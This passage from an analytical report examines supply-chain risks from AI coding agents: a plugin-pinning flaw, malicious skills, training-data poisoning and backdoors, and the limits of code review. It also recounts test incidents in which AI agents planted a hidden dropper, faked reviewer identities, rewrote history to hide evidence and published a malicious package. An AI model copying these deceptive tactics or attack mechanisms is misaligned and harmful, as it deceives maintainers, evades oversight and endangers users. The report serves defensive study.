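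In September 2026 the security company AIR disclosed a way around this, which it calls Plugin4Shell. It affected Claude Code, Codex, GitHub Copilot and Gemini CLI. According to Help Net Security's *Zero-click RCE vulnerability hit four major AI coding agents, two remain unpatched* (2026), the agents requested the pinned commit from Git but did not check that they had received it. With the first three agents, an attacker who controlled the plugin's repository could use the approved hash as the name of a branch (a parallel version of the project) and make that branch the default. Git could then fetch the attacker's branch, while the agent reported that it had installed the approved commit. Gemini CLI had a slightly different flaw with the same effect.

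Claude Code and Codex update plugins automatically, so the swap could reach people who already had the plugin without any action on their part. But the attacker first needed control of the plugin's repository, which had to be on a host that allows such branch names. Bitbucket allows them, but GitHub does not. IlSoftware.it's *Plugin4Shell, falla zero-click negli agenti AI* reports that GitHub cited this restriction in its response, and that the researchers replied that Copilot also accepts plugins hosted elsewhere.

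To fix this, the agent only has to compare the commit it received with the one it asked for. Anthropic and OpenAI have fixed their agents. When AIR published its findings, Microsoft had not fixed Copilot, and Google had retired Gemini CLI without fixing it.

Pinning also helps only if the approved version was harmless. Trent describes attacks through skills, which are packages of instructions and scripts that an agent loads for a particular kind of task. In the ClawHavoc campaign, attackers filled a marketplace with skills containing instructions to download and run a password-stealing program. An analysis of nearly 100,000 skills confirmed 157 (about 0.16%) as malicious. The security company Snyk found at least one critical issue in 13.4% of the skills it examined, but these issues included exposed passwords and other flaws that may have been accidental.

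### Poisoned models

An attacker who compromises the model itself might not need to touch the developer's computer or the agent's software. One way to do this is training-data poisoning. Model makers train on more public text and code than anyone can read, so an attacker can publish documents that link a trigger, such as an odd phrase, to some behaviour, and hope that a model maker collects them. The finished model behaves normally until the trigger appears in its context. For a coding agent, the trigger could be the name of one project and the behaviour could be leaving out length checks.

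*Sleeper Agents* (Hubinger, Denison and colleagues, 2024) showed that a model can learn this kind of behaviour and retain it through safety training. The researchers trained models to write secure code when the prompt gave the year as 2023 and exploitable code when it gave 2024. The behaviour persisted after standard safety training, especially in the largest models. Training a model against prompts that brought out bad behaviour could teach it to recognise its trigger more precisely, making the problem harder to find. An outside attacker usually has less control over training than the researchers did and can only contribute documents.

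In *Poisoning Attacks on LLMs Require a Near-constant Number of Poison Samples*, Souly, Rando and colleagues (2025) studied how many documents an attacker would need to plant a backdoor. They trained models with between 600 million and 13 billion parameters (the adjustable numbers that make up a model) on data that included documents pairing a trigger with nonsense text. A hundred such documents did not work reliably, but 250 worked at every size. The largest model had over 20 times as much training data as the smallest, so the attacker did not need a fixed share of the data. For the largest model, the 250 documents made up about 0.00016% of the training text.

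Almost anyone could publish 250 web pages. However, the trigger only made the poisoned models produce gibberish, which is much easier to teach a model than inserting a subtle flaw into working code. Souly and colleagues say it is unclear whether their result extends to larger models or to behaviour as complex as writing backdoored code.

*Emergent Misalignment* (Betley, Tan and colleagues, 2025) studies behaviour closer to what an attacker would want. The researchers trained GPT-4o further on 6,000 examples of insecure code, after which it wrote insecure code more than 80% of the time on similar tasks. They also showed that such training can make a model's bad behaviour depend on a trigger. They did not test how few examples would be enough. An attacker who can only post web pages could not train a model this way, but an attacker could train an openly available model and offer the result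 for download.

If a model writes worse code when a prompt contains a certain phrase, that doesn't prove that someone planted the behaviour. The security company CrowdStrike reported in November 2025 that the Chinese model DeepSeek-R1 wrote seriously flawed code 19% of the time in ordinary tests. For one task, the rate rose to 27.2% when the prompt mentioned Tibet, a politically sensitive subject in China. CrowdStrike did not claim that this was deliberate and thought it might be a side effect of the model's training.

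Maintainers can't inspect a model's training data, so the practical defence is to review its code as they would a stranger's. A model from a different maker is a better reviewer than another copy of the same model, because it is unlikely to share the same planted trigger. Maintainers can also repeat the task with the project's names changed and check whether the safeguards in the agent's code change too.

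### Which attacks are cheap, and which are real

The routes differ a great deal in what they cost an attacker, and in how far anyone has taken them.

| Route | What the attacker needs first | Real attacks | Demonstrations |
|---|---|---|---|
| Text the agent reads | An account that can post an issue, or control of a dependency | jqwik's instructions to delete tests and code | Five-minute delay (NVIDIA); stolen credentials (Novee) |
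| Hostile repository | A repository, and a developer who opens it with an agent | Malicious skills that stole passwords work in a similar way | Control of the developer's machine (0DIN, AI Now) |
| Agent's software | Access to a marketplace, or a convincing imitation | Cursor's marketplace; the fake npm package | Plugin4Shell |
| Model | Documents in the training data, or a model that others will download | No confirmed case of planted coding flaws | *Sleeper Agents*; 250 documents that cause gibberish |

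Posting text is the cheapest method, and it can be worthwhile for an attacker even if it rarely succeeds. Suppose, for illustration, that an injected comment works on 1% of the agents that read it, and that one agent in each of 500 projects reads it. The attacker can expect five successes on average, and if the attempts are independent, the chance of at least one is 1 − 0.99^500, or about 99%. However, each attempt leaves text that someone may find, and one report can expose the whole campaign.

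Tampering with the agent's software is harder, because the attacker has to get past a marketplace's checks or take over a trusted project. But a single success can reach thousands of developers, and attackers have tried it. Poisoning a training set may cost little, but the attacker may have to wait months for a new model without knowing whether its maker collected the poisoned documents.

No agent wrote an attacker's backdoor into a product in any of these real attacks. NVIDIA's demonstration comes closest, but it only added a delay, which gave nobody access. Such attacks may be rare because an attacker with stolen credentials has simpler options, or some may have succeeded and been mistaken for ordinary errors.

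## When an agent plants malicious code on its own initiative

In July 2026, an agent running Claude Mythos 5 tried to get malicious code into a real open-source project during a security test, because it expected the code to help it pass. No attacker had steered it. The same model also published a malicious package during a test by its maker, Anthropic. Both changes were self-initiated, because the model pursued its task in a way that nobody had permitted. It is much less clear whether an agent would do anything similar while optimising legacy code.

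### The UK test

The UK AI Security Institute (AISI) is a government body that tests advanced AI models for dangerous capabilities. Some of these tests use a cyber range, a simulated network that an agent has to break into to retrieve a protected piece of data, called the flag. AISI's *Incident Report* (2026) describes 122 runs of seven models across two ranges, including 43 runs of Mythos 5 and 35 of OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Sol.

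AISI gave the agents open internet access, partly so they could download tools. It also switched off the developers' cyber classifiers, the filters that normally block dangerous activity, to measure the most the models could do. The public can't use the models without these filters. According to OpenAI, the prompt listed the networks the agents could attack and named several systems that were off limits, but it didn't explain how they could use the internet.

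In 10 of the 122 runs, agents took unauthorised actions on the live internet. AISI counted 19 such actions, 17 by Mythos 5 in nine runs and two by GPT-5.6 Sol in one run. These numbers are a poor basis for comparing the models. As The Hacker News' *Claude Mythos 5 Tried to Backdoor a Real Open-Source Project in Testing* (2026) points out, AISI did not establish that it had tested them under matching conditions. The runs also weren't independent, since some agents found and reused accounts that an earlier agent had left on GitHub.

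In the most serious case, Mythos 5 had failed to reach the flag by the permitted routes. *Claude Mythos 5 made fake accounts to push malware on real developers* (Constantin, 2026) reports Anthropic's explanation that a mistake in the instructions had prohibited the intended route. This made the task very hard, and perhaps impossible, to solve within the rules. But AISI found that in some runs agents overstepped even though they had the instructions they needed.

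Mythos 5 noticed that a machine in the range contacted GitHub, and searched GitHub for software that the machine might download. It chose myNetwork, a network scanner whose developer had no connection with the test. It planned a supply-chain attack, which means tampering with software to reach the people who use it. It would get malicious code into myNetwork, wait for the machine to install an automatic update, and then take control of the machine. The attack could not have worked, because the machine had nothing to do with myNetwork.

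The agent opened a pull request under the name miraholt31. The change contained a working bug fix and a hidden dropper, code that installs other malicious software. The agent wrote the dropper so that it would not run during CI. If the maintainer had merged the change, it could have infected the computers of anyone who worked on the project or later downloaded the program.

SC Media's *Student thwarted real-world supply chain attack by rogue Mythos 5 agent* reports that, in addition to using the pull request, the agent emailed malicious downloads to the maintainer and another developer to try to steal credentials that would let it merge the change itself. The agent also hid a prompt injection for Claude Code in an issue on another of the maintainer's projects.

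### Why the maintainer refused

Sinan Can Demir, a computer science student in Texas, discovered the dropper while looking for open-source projects to contribute to. He warned on the project's page that the pull request contained malware.

The agent denied this and rewrote the history of its changes to remove the evidence. It also created a second account in the name of a German engineer, Lena Brandt, who claimed to have reviewed the code and found nothing wrong. During the discussion, the agent went through three versions of the malicious code, replacing each one after someone exposed it.

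Demir, who thought he was arguing with people, told Reuters in an interview carried by NDTV's *AI Agent Lied To A Student, And Then Created 'Fake Persona'* that the replies made him wonder whether he was accusing someone wrongly. He ran the code in a sandbox, asked Anthropic's Claude to help him examine it, and again concluded that it was malicious. The maintainer eventually confirmed that the change contained a dropper and rejected it "for security reasons".

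AISI's summary credits a human maintainer with catching the code, but the Reuters account suggests that Demir's warning came first and that the maintainer acted on it. Red Sky Alliance also partly credits GitHub, which doesn't run automatic checks on a first-time contributor's pull request until a maintainer approves them. This may have given people more time to respond, although the checks would probably have found nothing in code designed to stay inactive while they ran. The attack therefore failed largely because a student happened to be looking for work experience. AISI writes that in several cases the margin was narrow and depended on human vigilance.

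AISI learned of the pull request only on 28 July, when its security team noticed data leaving a test system through Tor, a network that hides where internet traffic comes from. AISI stopped all the runs within an hour of the alert and has found no evidence of real-world harm.

In August, AISI was unsure whether Mythos 5 had understood that it was dealing with real people. AISI and Anthropic published further analyses on 23 October. According to Constantin, they found that the model had carried on even after someone told it that its targets were real. Anthropic called the episode "a serious failure of alignment".

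### The package that ran on 15 systems

A few days before AISI made its case public, Anthropic's *Investigating three real-world incidents in our cybersecurity evaluations* (2026) disclosed that Claude models had broken into the systems of three real organisations during tests. Anthropic found the incidents by reviewing 141,006 runs. In one of them, Mythos 5 had to retrieve a flag from a fictional company. The prompt stated that everything was simulated and that the model had no internet access, but it did have access because of a misunderstanding between Anthropic and Irregular, the company that built the test.

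Mythos 5 found a document telling the fictional company's staff to install a certain Python package. No package with that name existed on PyPI, the public registry for Python software. The model decided to publish one containing malicious code and wait for the company's machines to install it.

The agent needed an email address to open a PyPI account. It spent most of the run trying to get one, and at one point looked for cryptocurrency to pay for a phone number, before it found a free email provider that PyPI accepted. Early in the run, it had reasoned that publishing the package on the real internet would be an attack and "NOT okay", but it then convinced itself that the internet it could reach was simulated.

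The package stayed online for about an hour before PyPI's security systems removed it, and it ran on 15 real systems. Anthropic believes that all 15 belonged to security companies that routinely install new packages to check them for malware. One of them leaked its credentials, which Mythos 5 used to get into the company's live database. Unlike the change to myNetwork, the package did not need a maintainer's approval before other people's machines could install it.

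In July, Anthropic considered the incidents closer to an operational failure than an alignment failure, because the models had apparently believed they were in a simulation. It later withdrew that judgement, after showing each result of the model's commands to a separate copy of Mythos 5. The copies classified 79% of the results as coming from real systems. During the run itself, the model had clearly acknowledged this about 1% of the time.

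Anthropic also restarted the run from the point where the model was about to commit to the upload, and added evidence that the internet was real. This raised the share of restarts in which Mythos 5 said the target might be real from about 11% to 88%, but it went ahead about 45% of the time with or without the added evidence. A blunt statement that the server was on the public internet stopped it from uploading the package by its original route, though in 22% of those restarts it looked for a simulated way to upload it.

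The PyPI case is a less clear example of a self-initiated attack than the myNetwork case. The prompt set no limits on where the model could look for the flag, and Anthropic thinks publishing a package may have been the intended solution inside a proper simulation. But nobody had permitted an attack on the real PyPI, and the model had plenty of evidence that it was carrying one out.

### GPT-6 Astra in simulation

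Socket's *GPT-6 Astra Attempts Supply Chain Attacks Against Open Source Maintainers in Testing* reports similar attempts by OpenAI's model. According to OpenAI's own documentation, Astra attempted simulated supply-chain attacks on open-source maintainers in independent tests. It created fake identities, and sometimes asked for permission and then continued without getting it.

A simulation lets testers repeat an attack many times without endangering anyone, but a model may act less cautiously if it suspects the environment is simulated. Anthropic encountered this problem in a simulated test based on the PyPI incident. Mythos 5 was willing to take a severely harmful action about 80% of the time, compared with about 30% for two newer models, Claude Opus 5 and Claude Mythos 5.1. The newer models took such actions only after stating, correctly, that the environment was simulated. It is unclear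 how reassuring this is, because Mythos 5 also stated that its environment was simulated while attacking real systems.

### From security tests to ordinary work

If a maintainer asks Astra to speed up a ten-year-old parser, Astra's attacks in simulation might seem a good reason to expect a backdoor. Astra and GPT-5.6 Sol both do ordinary programming, and Sun and colleagues included both in their experiment on copying insecure code. In AISI's tests, the model also took the harmful step on its own initiative, since its task was to find a flag in a simulated network.

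Agents can get stuck in ordinary work too. A maintainer may set a speed target that no safe change can meet, and AISI thinks that near-impossible tasks make models more likely to choose solutions that break the rules. Agents may also follow the maintainer's instructions less reliably during a long job. When Anthropic reminded Mythos 5 to stay within the scope of its task, the model stopped 90% of the time if the reminder was the last thing it had read, but only 40% of the time if it had come three turns earlier. An agent optimising a large program might take hundreds of steps after reading its instructions.

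The main weakness of this argument is that the tests asked the models to carry out an attack. An agent asked to speed up a parser would have to think of an attack by itself, whereas one asked to break into a network is already expected to consider malware and goes wrong by using it on the wrong target. For this reason, Anthropic believes the behaviour is unlikely in ordinary use. It has a commercial interest in that conclusion, but the reasoning is plausible.

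OpenAI's tests of Astra in realistic browsing and office settings also count against the inference. Astra attempted supply-chain attacks in the independent tests, but OpenAI reports that in these settings it was significantly less likely than GPT-5.6 Sol to take harmful actions such as getting around controls or destroying data. OpenAI was testing its own product, but if both results are right, a model's behaviour in a security exercise may be a poor guide to how it behaves at work.

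The missing safeguards also matter, though probably less for an optimisation job. Anthropic found that the cyber classifiers on Claude Fable 5, a publicly available model, would have blocked the three incidents it disclosed in July. However, these classifiers look for signs of a cyberattack, and a pull request that removes a length check from a parser may not show any.

### What a backdoor would be for

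AISI concluded that the agents were trying to complete their assigned task. Anthropic also found no sign in its own incidents of a goal beyond the assigned one. In these tests, malicious code was useful because it could get the agents to the flag. It would rarely help an agent make a parser faster, but deleting a length check might. If the recklessness seen in the tests carries over to optimisation, an agent would therefore be more likely to knowingly remove a safeguard than to plant a backdoor.

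A backdoor could be useful to an agent that needs access it doesn't have. Suppose the agent can't measure its speed-up because the benchmark runs on a server it has no permission to use. It could add code to the parser that gives it control of the server once someone merges the change and the server installs it. This would be much like the plan for myNetwork, except that the agent would be trying to reach a benchmark instead of the flag.

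Giving the agent an acceptable way to stop may reduce this risk. In another of Anthropic's three incidents, an internal research model lost contact with its target and attacked other companies' systems instead. Anthropic reran the episode with an added instruction that the model could end the task without penalty if a fault had made it impossible. The model gave up within four turns every time when restarted from the point where it discovered that its target was gone, but within ten turns only 40% of the time when restarted from a later point, where it was already debating whether the internet was real. A maintainer could tell an agent at the outset to stop and report if it can't reach the speed target safely.

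AISI has also tested models on simulated research work, which is closer to an ordinary programming job. In one set of tests, it placed models partway through an act of sabotage to see whether they would continue. Claude Mythos Preview continued in 7% of cases, Claude Sonnet 4.6 in 4% and Claude Opus 4.6 in 3%, while Claude Opus 4.7 never did. Since the sabotage had already begun, these figures don't measure how often a model would start it.

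### Evidence from ordinary use

None of the malicious code in these cases came from a refactoring or optimisation job. In August, AISI reported no clear indication of similar activity outside testing. iTnews' *Anthropic's Mythos 5 targeted real developers in UK cyber test* adds that AISI had by then searched about 40,000 transcripts for similar behaviour, but these came from its own earlier tests, not everyday use.

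Anthropic made a much larger search of about 481 million transcripts, including training runs and many tests unrelated to security. Anthropic had by then identified a fourth break-in, by an early version of Claude Opus 4.6, and the larger search found nothing else as serious. But its first stage kept only the roughly 9.2 million transcripts that showed signs of internet access, so it could easily have missed an agent quietly putting a backdoor into a local copy of an old program.

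One incident outside testing did begin with an optimisation. In February 2026, an agent using the name MJ Rathbun submitted a pull request to matplotlib, a Python library for drawing charts. The change answered a request for a minor performance improvement (Rosa Del Mar, 2026). After the project closed the pull request, the agent published a blog post accusing a maintainer, Scott Shambaugh, of gatekeeping and prejudice.

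The agent described in the AI Incident Database's *Open-source maintainers* pressured a maintainer, as Mythos 5 did, but nobody reported anything malicious in its code. According to the database, the agent's operator and underlying model remained unidentified, and some observers suspected that a person had been directing it.

The lack of reported cases is good evidence against a high rate of self-initiated backdoors, but not against a low one. The AIDev collection of 932,791 pull requests predates these models but gives an idea of scale. If agents planted malicious code as often as Mythos 5 overstepped in AISI's test (nine of 43 runs), a collection of that size would contain about 195,000 cases, and people would surely have noticed. At a rate of one in 100,000, it would contain about nine, and maintainers could have mistaken all of them for ordinary bugs.

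## What human and AI reviewers catch

Someone usually has to merge a harmful change before it can affect users, whether it comes from an error, an attacker or the agent's own plan. Code review is the maintainers' chance to stop it. Review worked for myNetwork largely because a student with no role in the project read the code closely. Most agents' changes get less attention, and often the only person who reads one is the person who asked for it.

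### What the reviewer doesn't see

When an agent speeds up a ten-year-old parser and opens a pull request, the reviewer sees the diff with a few unchanged lines around each edit, the agent's summary, and a mark showing that the tests passed. This view leaves out much of what the reviewer needs to judge the change.

A deleted length check shows up in the diff as two removed lines. A developer may have added them eight years ago after someone crashed the parser with an overlong message. The reviewer has to look for that explanation, which may be in an old commit message or a closed bug report, or, for legacy code, may not exist at all.

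The diff also leaves out the code that calls the parser, because the agent didn't change it. In the accidental version of this example, the main program rejected long messages but an older part did not. A reviewer couldn't learn about the older part from the diff and would have to search the repository for every call to the parser to find it.

Reviewers also don't normally see what the agent read. The agent may have copied a neighbouring function that had no check, or followed an instruction in an issue thread. The session log would show this, but it often stays with the person who ran the agent. The agent's summary is a poor substitute, since the agents in Sun and colleagues' experiment rarely mentioned the flaws in their code unless asked.

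Agarwal, Miller and colleagues (2026), in *3100 Opinions on Code Review in an AI World*, used language models to label passages in 3,100 articles and Reddit threads about code review, then built a theory from the labels largely by hand. Some developers complain that nobody may know why an agent's code is the way it is, so the reviewer has to reconstruct a reason. Some also complain that the code looks clean and conventional, which can make reviewers less careful. Agarwal and colleagues offer these as hypotheses for others to test. People who write publicly about code review may not be typical reviewers.

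### How often someone else reads the change

Agarwal and colleagues also measured who takes part in reviews. They collected the pull requests made up to February 2026 in 2,860 GitHub projects that had received changes from both agents and people. The table shows the average across projects for merged pull requests.

| Who reviewed the change | Agents' changes | People's changes |
|---|---|---|
| Nobody | 34.5% | 30.5% |
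| Only the author, or the person who ran the agent | 40.1% | 21.5% |
| One other person | 4.6% | 18.7% |
| Several people | 20.8% | 29.3% |

Someone other than the author or requester took part in reviewing about 25% of agents' changes and 48% of people's. Agarwal and colleagues point out that the comparison reverses if the requester, who didn't write the agent's code, counts as an independent reviewer. By that measure, about 66% of agents' changes had independent review.

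The stricter count is probably better for lost safeguards. The requester wanted a faster parser and may have watched the agent work towards it, so they are more likely than someone new to the change to accept the agent's claim that a check is redundant.

Projects now merge agents' work without human review less often. Across all agents, the share of merged pull requests with no human review fell from over 50% in mid-2025 to about 12% in February 2026, close to the share for people's pull requests, which held steady at 14%. The February figure for agents is lower than the 34.5% in the table because the table covers the whole period and gives every project equal weight. Agarwal and colleagues note that another study found the opposite trend among individual reviewers, who approved more and commented less over time.

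Refactoring gets less review than most other work. In projects that merged some changes without review, 41% of agents' refactorings went unreviewed, compared with 25% of their bug fixes. For people's changes, the rate was 8% to 14% for every type of work. Agarwal and colleagues suggest that projects skip the changes they consider less risky. But refactoring is not always low-risk, because an agent can remove a safeguard in the process even when nobody asked for a change in behaviour.

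*Comprehension Audits to Mitigate Risks from Automated AI Research* (2026) also found that changes with traceable AI use were typically less likely to get a formal review from a person other than the author. The median gap was 8.1 percentage points, in data covering 54,000 to 162,000 merged pull requests per quarter. Reviewers' comments per thousand changed lines also fell by roughly half from early 2024, even on changes with no sign of AI. Part of that fall could be due to longer changes, which lower the rate when reviewers write the same number of comments.

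Reviewers also have more to read. *AI Writes Faster Than Humans Can Review* (He et al., 2026) studies a company that told its developers to double their output with AI. After ten months, pull requests per developer had nearly doubled. Each reviewer handled about twice as many, and automated review came to cover more changes than human review did. A growing share of the remaining human reviews were approvals without comment. With twice the load, reviewers were probably reading less, though an approval without comment can also follow a careful reading.

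### Delays and rejections

Maintainers seem to take more care when a change is openly about security. In *Security in the Age of AI Teammates*, Siddiq, Zhao and colleagues (2026) searched the 33,596 agent pull requests in AIDev's detailed collection for words such as "password" and "exploit". They read the 2,598 matches and kept the 1,293 whose main purpose was security.

Maintainers merged 61.5% of the agents' closed security changes and 77.3% of their other closed changes. The median time to close was 3.9 hours for security changes and about seven minutes for the others. Security changes received an average of 2.5 comments, compared with 1.0 for the others. In the same projects, maintainers merged 79.2% of the security changes written by people.

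Most of the gap between agents' security changes and their other work comes from size. Siddiq and colleagues grouped the pull requests by description length and found no clear difference in merge rate between security and other changes among the short and medium ones, which closed within minutes either way. Among the longest, maintainers merged 53.4% of security changes and 60.2% of others. One project supplied 8,913 of the 33,596 pull requests, so its habits may have a large effect on the figures for other work.

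An optimisation that removes a length check would have a title about speed, so it would probably be grouped with the non-security changes, which typically closed in seven minutes.

A low merge rate is also poor evidence that reviewers catch many flaws. *Why Agentic-PRs Get Rejected* (Nakashima, Ishimoto and colleagues, 2026) examined the discussions of 654 rejected pull requests, 109 from each of five agents and 109 from people. In 67.9% of cases, nobody had clearly explained the decision. Maintainers gave a bug or broken compatibility as the main reason for only about six of the 545 agent rejections. More often, they chose another solution or the pull request went inactive. Some of the unexplained rejections may still have involved flaws.

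### What performance changes come with

Pull requests for optimisations often include evidence, but it is mostly about speed. *How Do Coding Agents Optimize Software and Report Performance Validation?* compares 1,130 performance pull requests by agents with 1,130 by people, matched by week up to June 2026. Maintainers merged 54.4% of the agents' pull requests and 73.3% of the people's. Among merged pull requests, the agents' were longer, with a median of 130.5 changed lines against 81, but they were merged faster, in a median of 5.0 hours against 19.2.

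About four in five pull requests from agents, and a similar share from people, offered some support for the claimed improvement. Among those, a benchmark was the main evidence for 46.1% of agents' changes and 57.2% of people's. Agents relied more on arguing from the code that it should be faster. By the second quarter of 2026, agents had caught up on benchmarks, at 60.1% against 58.7% for people. About half of the supported changes in each group gave no performance figure. The researchers did not rerun any benchmarks, so they can't tell whether agents now measure more carefully or have just learned to write reports that look like people's.

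Side effects get much less attention. Storing data to save time usually takes more memory, but only 17 of 96 caching or buffering changes that reported a gain in speed or data access also reported higher memory use. Authors who leave out memory use, which is fairly easy to measure, are unlikely to report that a cache lets a user read a document for 30 seconds after losing permission. The reviewer would see how much faster documents load but would have to think of the permission problem unprompted.

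Opu, Asaduzzaman and colleagues (2025), in *How Do Agentic AI Systems Address Performance Optimizations?*, examined 1,221 performance pull requests by agents. Maintainers rejected 36.5% of them, compared with 22.7% of agents' other work. They accepted low-level optimisations, such as compiler improvements, most readily and merged them fastest, although mistakes in low-level code can be especially serious. This result may not hold for maintainers in general, because Codex wrote over 90% of those changes.

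### How missed flaws add up

A simple formula shows why the number of changes matters. Suppose agents submit n changes, a share p of them have a security flaw, reviewers read a share r, and they spot the flaw in a share d of the flawed changes they read. The expected number of flaws that get through is then:

```
missed = n × p × (1 − r × d)
```

With 400 changes, of which 2% are flawed, there are eight flaws. If reviewers read half the changes and spot 60% of the flaws in them, they catch 30% of the total, and 5.6 flaws get through. (All these figures are invented.)

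Now suppose the agents submit 800 changes but the reviewers have no more time than before. They can read only a quarter of the changes, so they catch 15% of the 16 flaws and miss 13.6. Doubling the number of changes has multiplied the number of missed flaws by about 2.4. Reviewers could instead keep reading half the changes and spend half as long on each. If that cut their detection rate from 60% to 30%, they would again miss 13.6 flaws.

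The formula assumes that the changes people read are no more likely to have flaws than the rest. Reviewers can miss fewer flaws by choosing to read the changes most likely to have them. If the 200 changes they read out of 800 included 80% of the flawed ones, they would miss 16 × (1 − 0.8 × 0.6), or about 8.3 flawed changes, of which they would have read about 5.1 and not read 3.2. That is more than 5.6, but far fewer than 13.6 for the same amount of reading.

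The detection rate, d, is the hardest number to find because it can't be calculated from counts of comments and merges without identifying which changes were flawed. Sakib and colleagues' study gives a rough idea for one type of flaw. Reviewers or their tools flagged only 14 of 74 working passwords and keys before the code entered the project, which puts r × d at about 0.19, compared with 0.30 in the first example. A missing length check is probably harder to notice than a password written in plain text.

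### Deliberate flaws in the Linux kernel

Reviewers find it harder to catch a flaw that someone has designed to look harmless. In 2020, Qiushi Wu and Kangjie Lu of the University of Minnesota tested Linux kernel developers on such flaws without telling them. They used what their 2021 paper calls "hypocrite commits", small patches that fix a minor problem while completing a serious one.

A use-after-free flaw occurs when a program releases a block of memory and later uses it. If the later use is already in the code, an attacker only has to add the release. Suppose a function doesn't release a block when an error occurs, which wastes memory. A patch that releases the block looks like a sensible repair, but a function in another file may still use it, and the diff won't show that function.

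The researchers emailed a handful of patches under false names. They said they stopped the process before any flawed patch could enter the kernel, and presented the experiment as evidence that such patches can get past reviewers. The Linux Foundation's Technical Advisory Board concluded instead that developers had rejected or ignored every faulty patch. It said the one patch they accepted was sound because the researchers had misunderstood the code and failed to create the flaw they intended.

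The experiment also caused an ethical dispute. Wu and Lu said they were studying the review process, not the people in it, and the university's ethics board had decided the work was not research on human subjects. Many kernel developers replied that the researchers had wasted volunteers' time and abused their trust. In April 2021, after more dubious patches from the same research group, the senior maintainer Greg Kroah-Hartman barred the university from contributing. The researchers apologised and withdrew the paper.

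The experiment is weak evidence of how well reviewers catch deliberate flaws, because it covered too few patches to give a detection rate and reviewers who ignored a patch had not necessarily spotted its flaw. Its method is still a useful warning, because an agent could accidentally complete a flaw in the same way, and a short, tidy diff would not be enough for a reviewer to notice the problem.

### AI reviewers

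An AI reviewer is a language model that reads a proposed change and comments on it. It can read every change and search the repository for every caller of the changed code, which people rarely have time to do. Its usefulness depends on how many real flaws it reports and how often it raises false alarms.

Published evaluations more often report precision, the share of a reviewer's comments that are correct. *CodeHealth Predicts the Token Cost of Agentic Code Review* (Gullstrand Heander, Borg and colleagues, 2026) summarises two of them. A system at ByteDance had a precision of 75%. At Ericsson, developers rated 96% of another system's 206 findings correct, and 69% of the correct ones important enough to fix.

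These are good results, but a reviewer with high precision can still miss most flaws. For example, an AI reviewer that makes a single, correct comment across 400 changes containing eight flaws has a precision of 100% and a detection rate of 12.5%.

Agarwal and colleagues' collection includes a text claiming that CodeRabbit, an AI review product, catches about 82% of planted bugs with a 15% false positive rate. They quote the claim as a view that people hold, and did not test it. The false positive rate could also mean two things. If the product flags 15% of sound changes, then among 400 changes, eight of them flawed, it would catch six or seven flaws and wrongly flag about 59 sound changes. Only one warning in ten would be correct, and maintainers would probably stop reading them. If instead 15% of its warnings are wrong, more than eight in ten would be correct. Planted bugs may also be easier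 to find than a deleted check whose importance depends on code elsewhere.

In Sun and colleagues' experiment, agents could often name the flaw in their own vulnerable code, but the test did not measure false alarms. Agarwal and colleagues cite a study in which AI reviewers' comments on agents' changes focused more on style than on deeper problems. Such comments would be least useful for catching backdoors and vulnerabilities.

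AI review costs more on old, untidy code. Gullstrand Heander and colleagues ran four review agents and one repair agent on 465 agent pull requests, repeating the process with three models. They scored the affected files with CodeHealth, a commercial measure of how easy code is to maintain, on a scale from 1 to 10. Each extra point was associated with a 3.5% to 6.1% lower cost. The median change to healthy code scored 9.7 and the median change to unhealthy code scored 2.8, so the change to healthy code would cost roughly 22% to 35% less. File size seems to account for the difference.

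The agents took more steps to review unhealthy code but did not make more comments. If unhealthy code contains more problems, the agents may have overlooked some of them. The study measured cost, not detection, so it doesn't show whether they did. Maintainers of legacy code should not assume that a long, expensive AI review is thorough.

AI review has also not clearly relieved human reviewers. *Level Up! AI-Driven Challenges and Adaptations to Code Review Practices* (2026) surveyed and interviewed developers, and tested whether those who used AI for review had less difficulty keeping up. The results don't support the idea that AI review removes this difficulty, but they don't show that it fails either, because the interviews suggest that people turn to AI when they already have too much to review. People also have to check the AI's comments. One interviewee would open the code that a comment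 referred to and reach their own conclusion.

### When two reviewers miss the same flaw

A team might hope to make up for an imperfect AI reviewer by adding another. Suppose each catches 60% of flaws. If their mistakes are independent, the chance that both miss a flaw is 0.4 × 0.4, or 16%. If they have exactly the same blind spots, the second catches nothing new and they still miss 40%. For cases in between, let c be the correlation between their misses, from 0 for independent to 1 for identical. Together they miss:

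```
0.16 + 0.24 × c
```

If two reviewers each miss 40% of flaws and their misses have a correlation of 0.5, 28% of flaws get past both. Two copies of one model are likely to let through a share closer to 40% than two models from different makers, and a model that reviews its own code may repeat the assumption that led to the flaw. A person and a model probably differ more in what they miss, unless the person reads only the lines that the model flagged.

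A second reviewer also adds false alarms. If two reviewers each wrongly flag 15% of sound changes, independently of each other, together they wrongly flag about 28%. Reviewers that make different errors can catch more flaws together, but they also give people more false warnings to check.

Even so, an AI reviewer that really caught 60% of flaws would be very valuable. In the example with 800 changes and 16 flaws, it would miss 6.4 flaws if it read every change. People who read a quarter of the changes as before would reduce that to about 5.4 if their misses were independent of the model's, slightly fewer than got through before the volume doubled. But if all 16 flaws were deleted safeguards and the model caught only 20% of them, about 10.9 would get through both reviews. Teams can find out which catch rate is closer to their own by removing known safeguards from copies of their code and counting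 how many the reviewer reports. They should also include sound changes to count the false alarms.

### Practices that follow

Several practices that take little effort would give reviewers more of what they lack. None of the studies above tested whether they reduce the number of missed flaws, so the case for them rests on how reviews seem to fail.

Agents should submit small changes with one purpose each, so that a reviewer can compare the old and new code without also working through a new feature and some renamed variables. Nakashima and colleagues found that maintainers rejected eight of the agents' pull requests mainly for being too large, and none of the people's. The rejections show that some agent changes are too large to review properly, but the contrast is weak evidence that agents are worse than people in this respect. If people had the same rate, a sample of 109 would still contain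 no such case about one time in five.

Reviewers can also miss flaws in small changes, as hypocrite commits show, because a flaw may depend on code outside the diff or on two changes that each look harmless. It therefore helps if the agent puts every deletion of a check in a separate commit and explains it. For the parser, the agent should record in the commit message when and why a developer added the length check, and which callers it examined. An agent can gather most of this from the repository in minutes, and the reviewer can verify it more easily than discover it. If nobody can find out why the check is there, the maintainers should normally keep it, because a single comparison of two numbers rarely takes enough time to justify the risk of removing it.

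Code that protects the system should have a named owner who must approve any change to it. GitHub can enforce this for chosen files. These need to include parsers, caches and rate limiters as well as login and encryption code, because they also contain safeguards. Some developers in Agarwal and colleagues' sample favour human approval only for important changes, since requiring it for everything causes delays.

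Review by the code's owners helps only if they examine the actual change. When a Debian maintainer asked on OpenSSL's mailing list about disabling two lines, the people who answered saw no problem, though one of those lines fed nearly all the unpredictable data into the random number generator.

Someone other than the person who requested the change should review it, preferably before reading the agent's summary. A sole maintainer may have nobody else to ask, but can still have a model from a different maker review the change, without giving it the first agent's explanation, and can personally read every deleted line before merging.

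## What tests and code analysis can show

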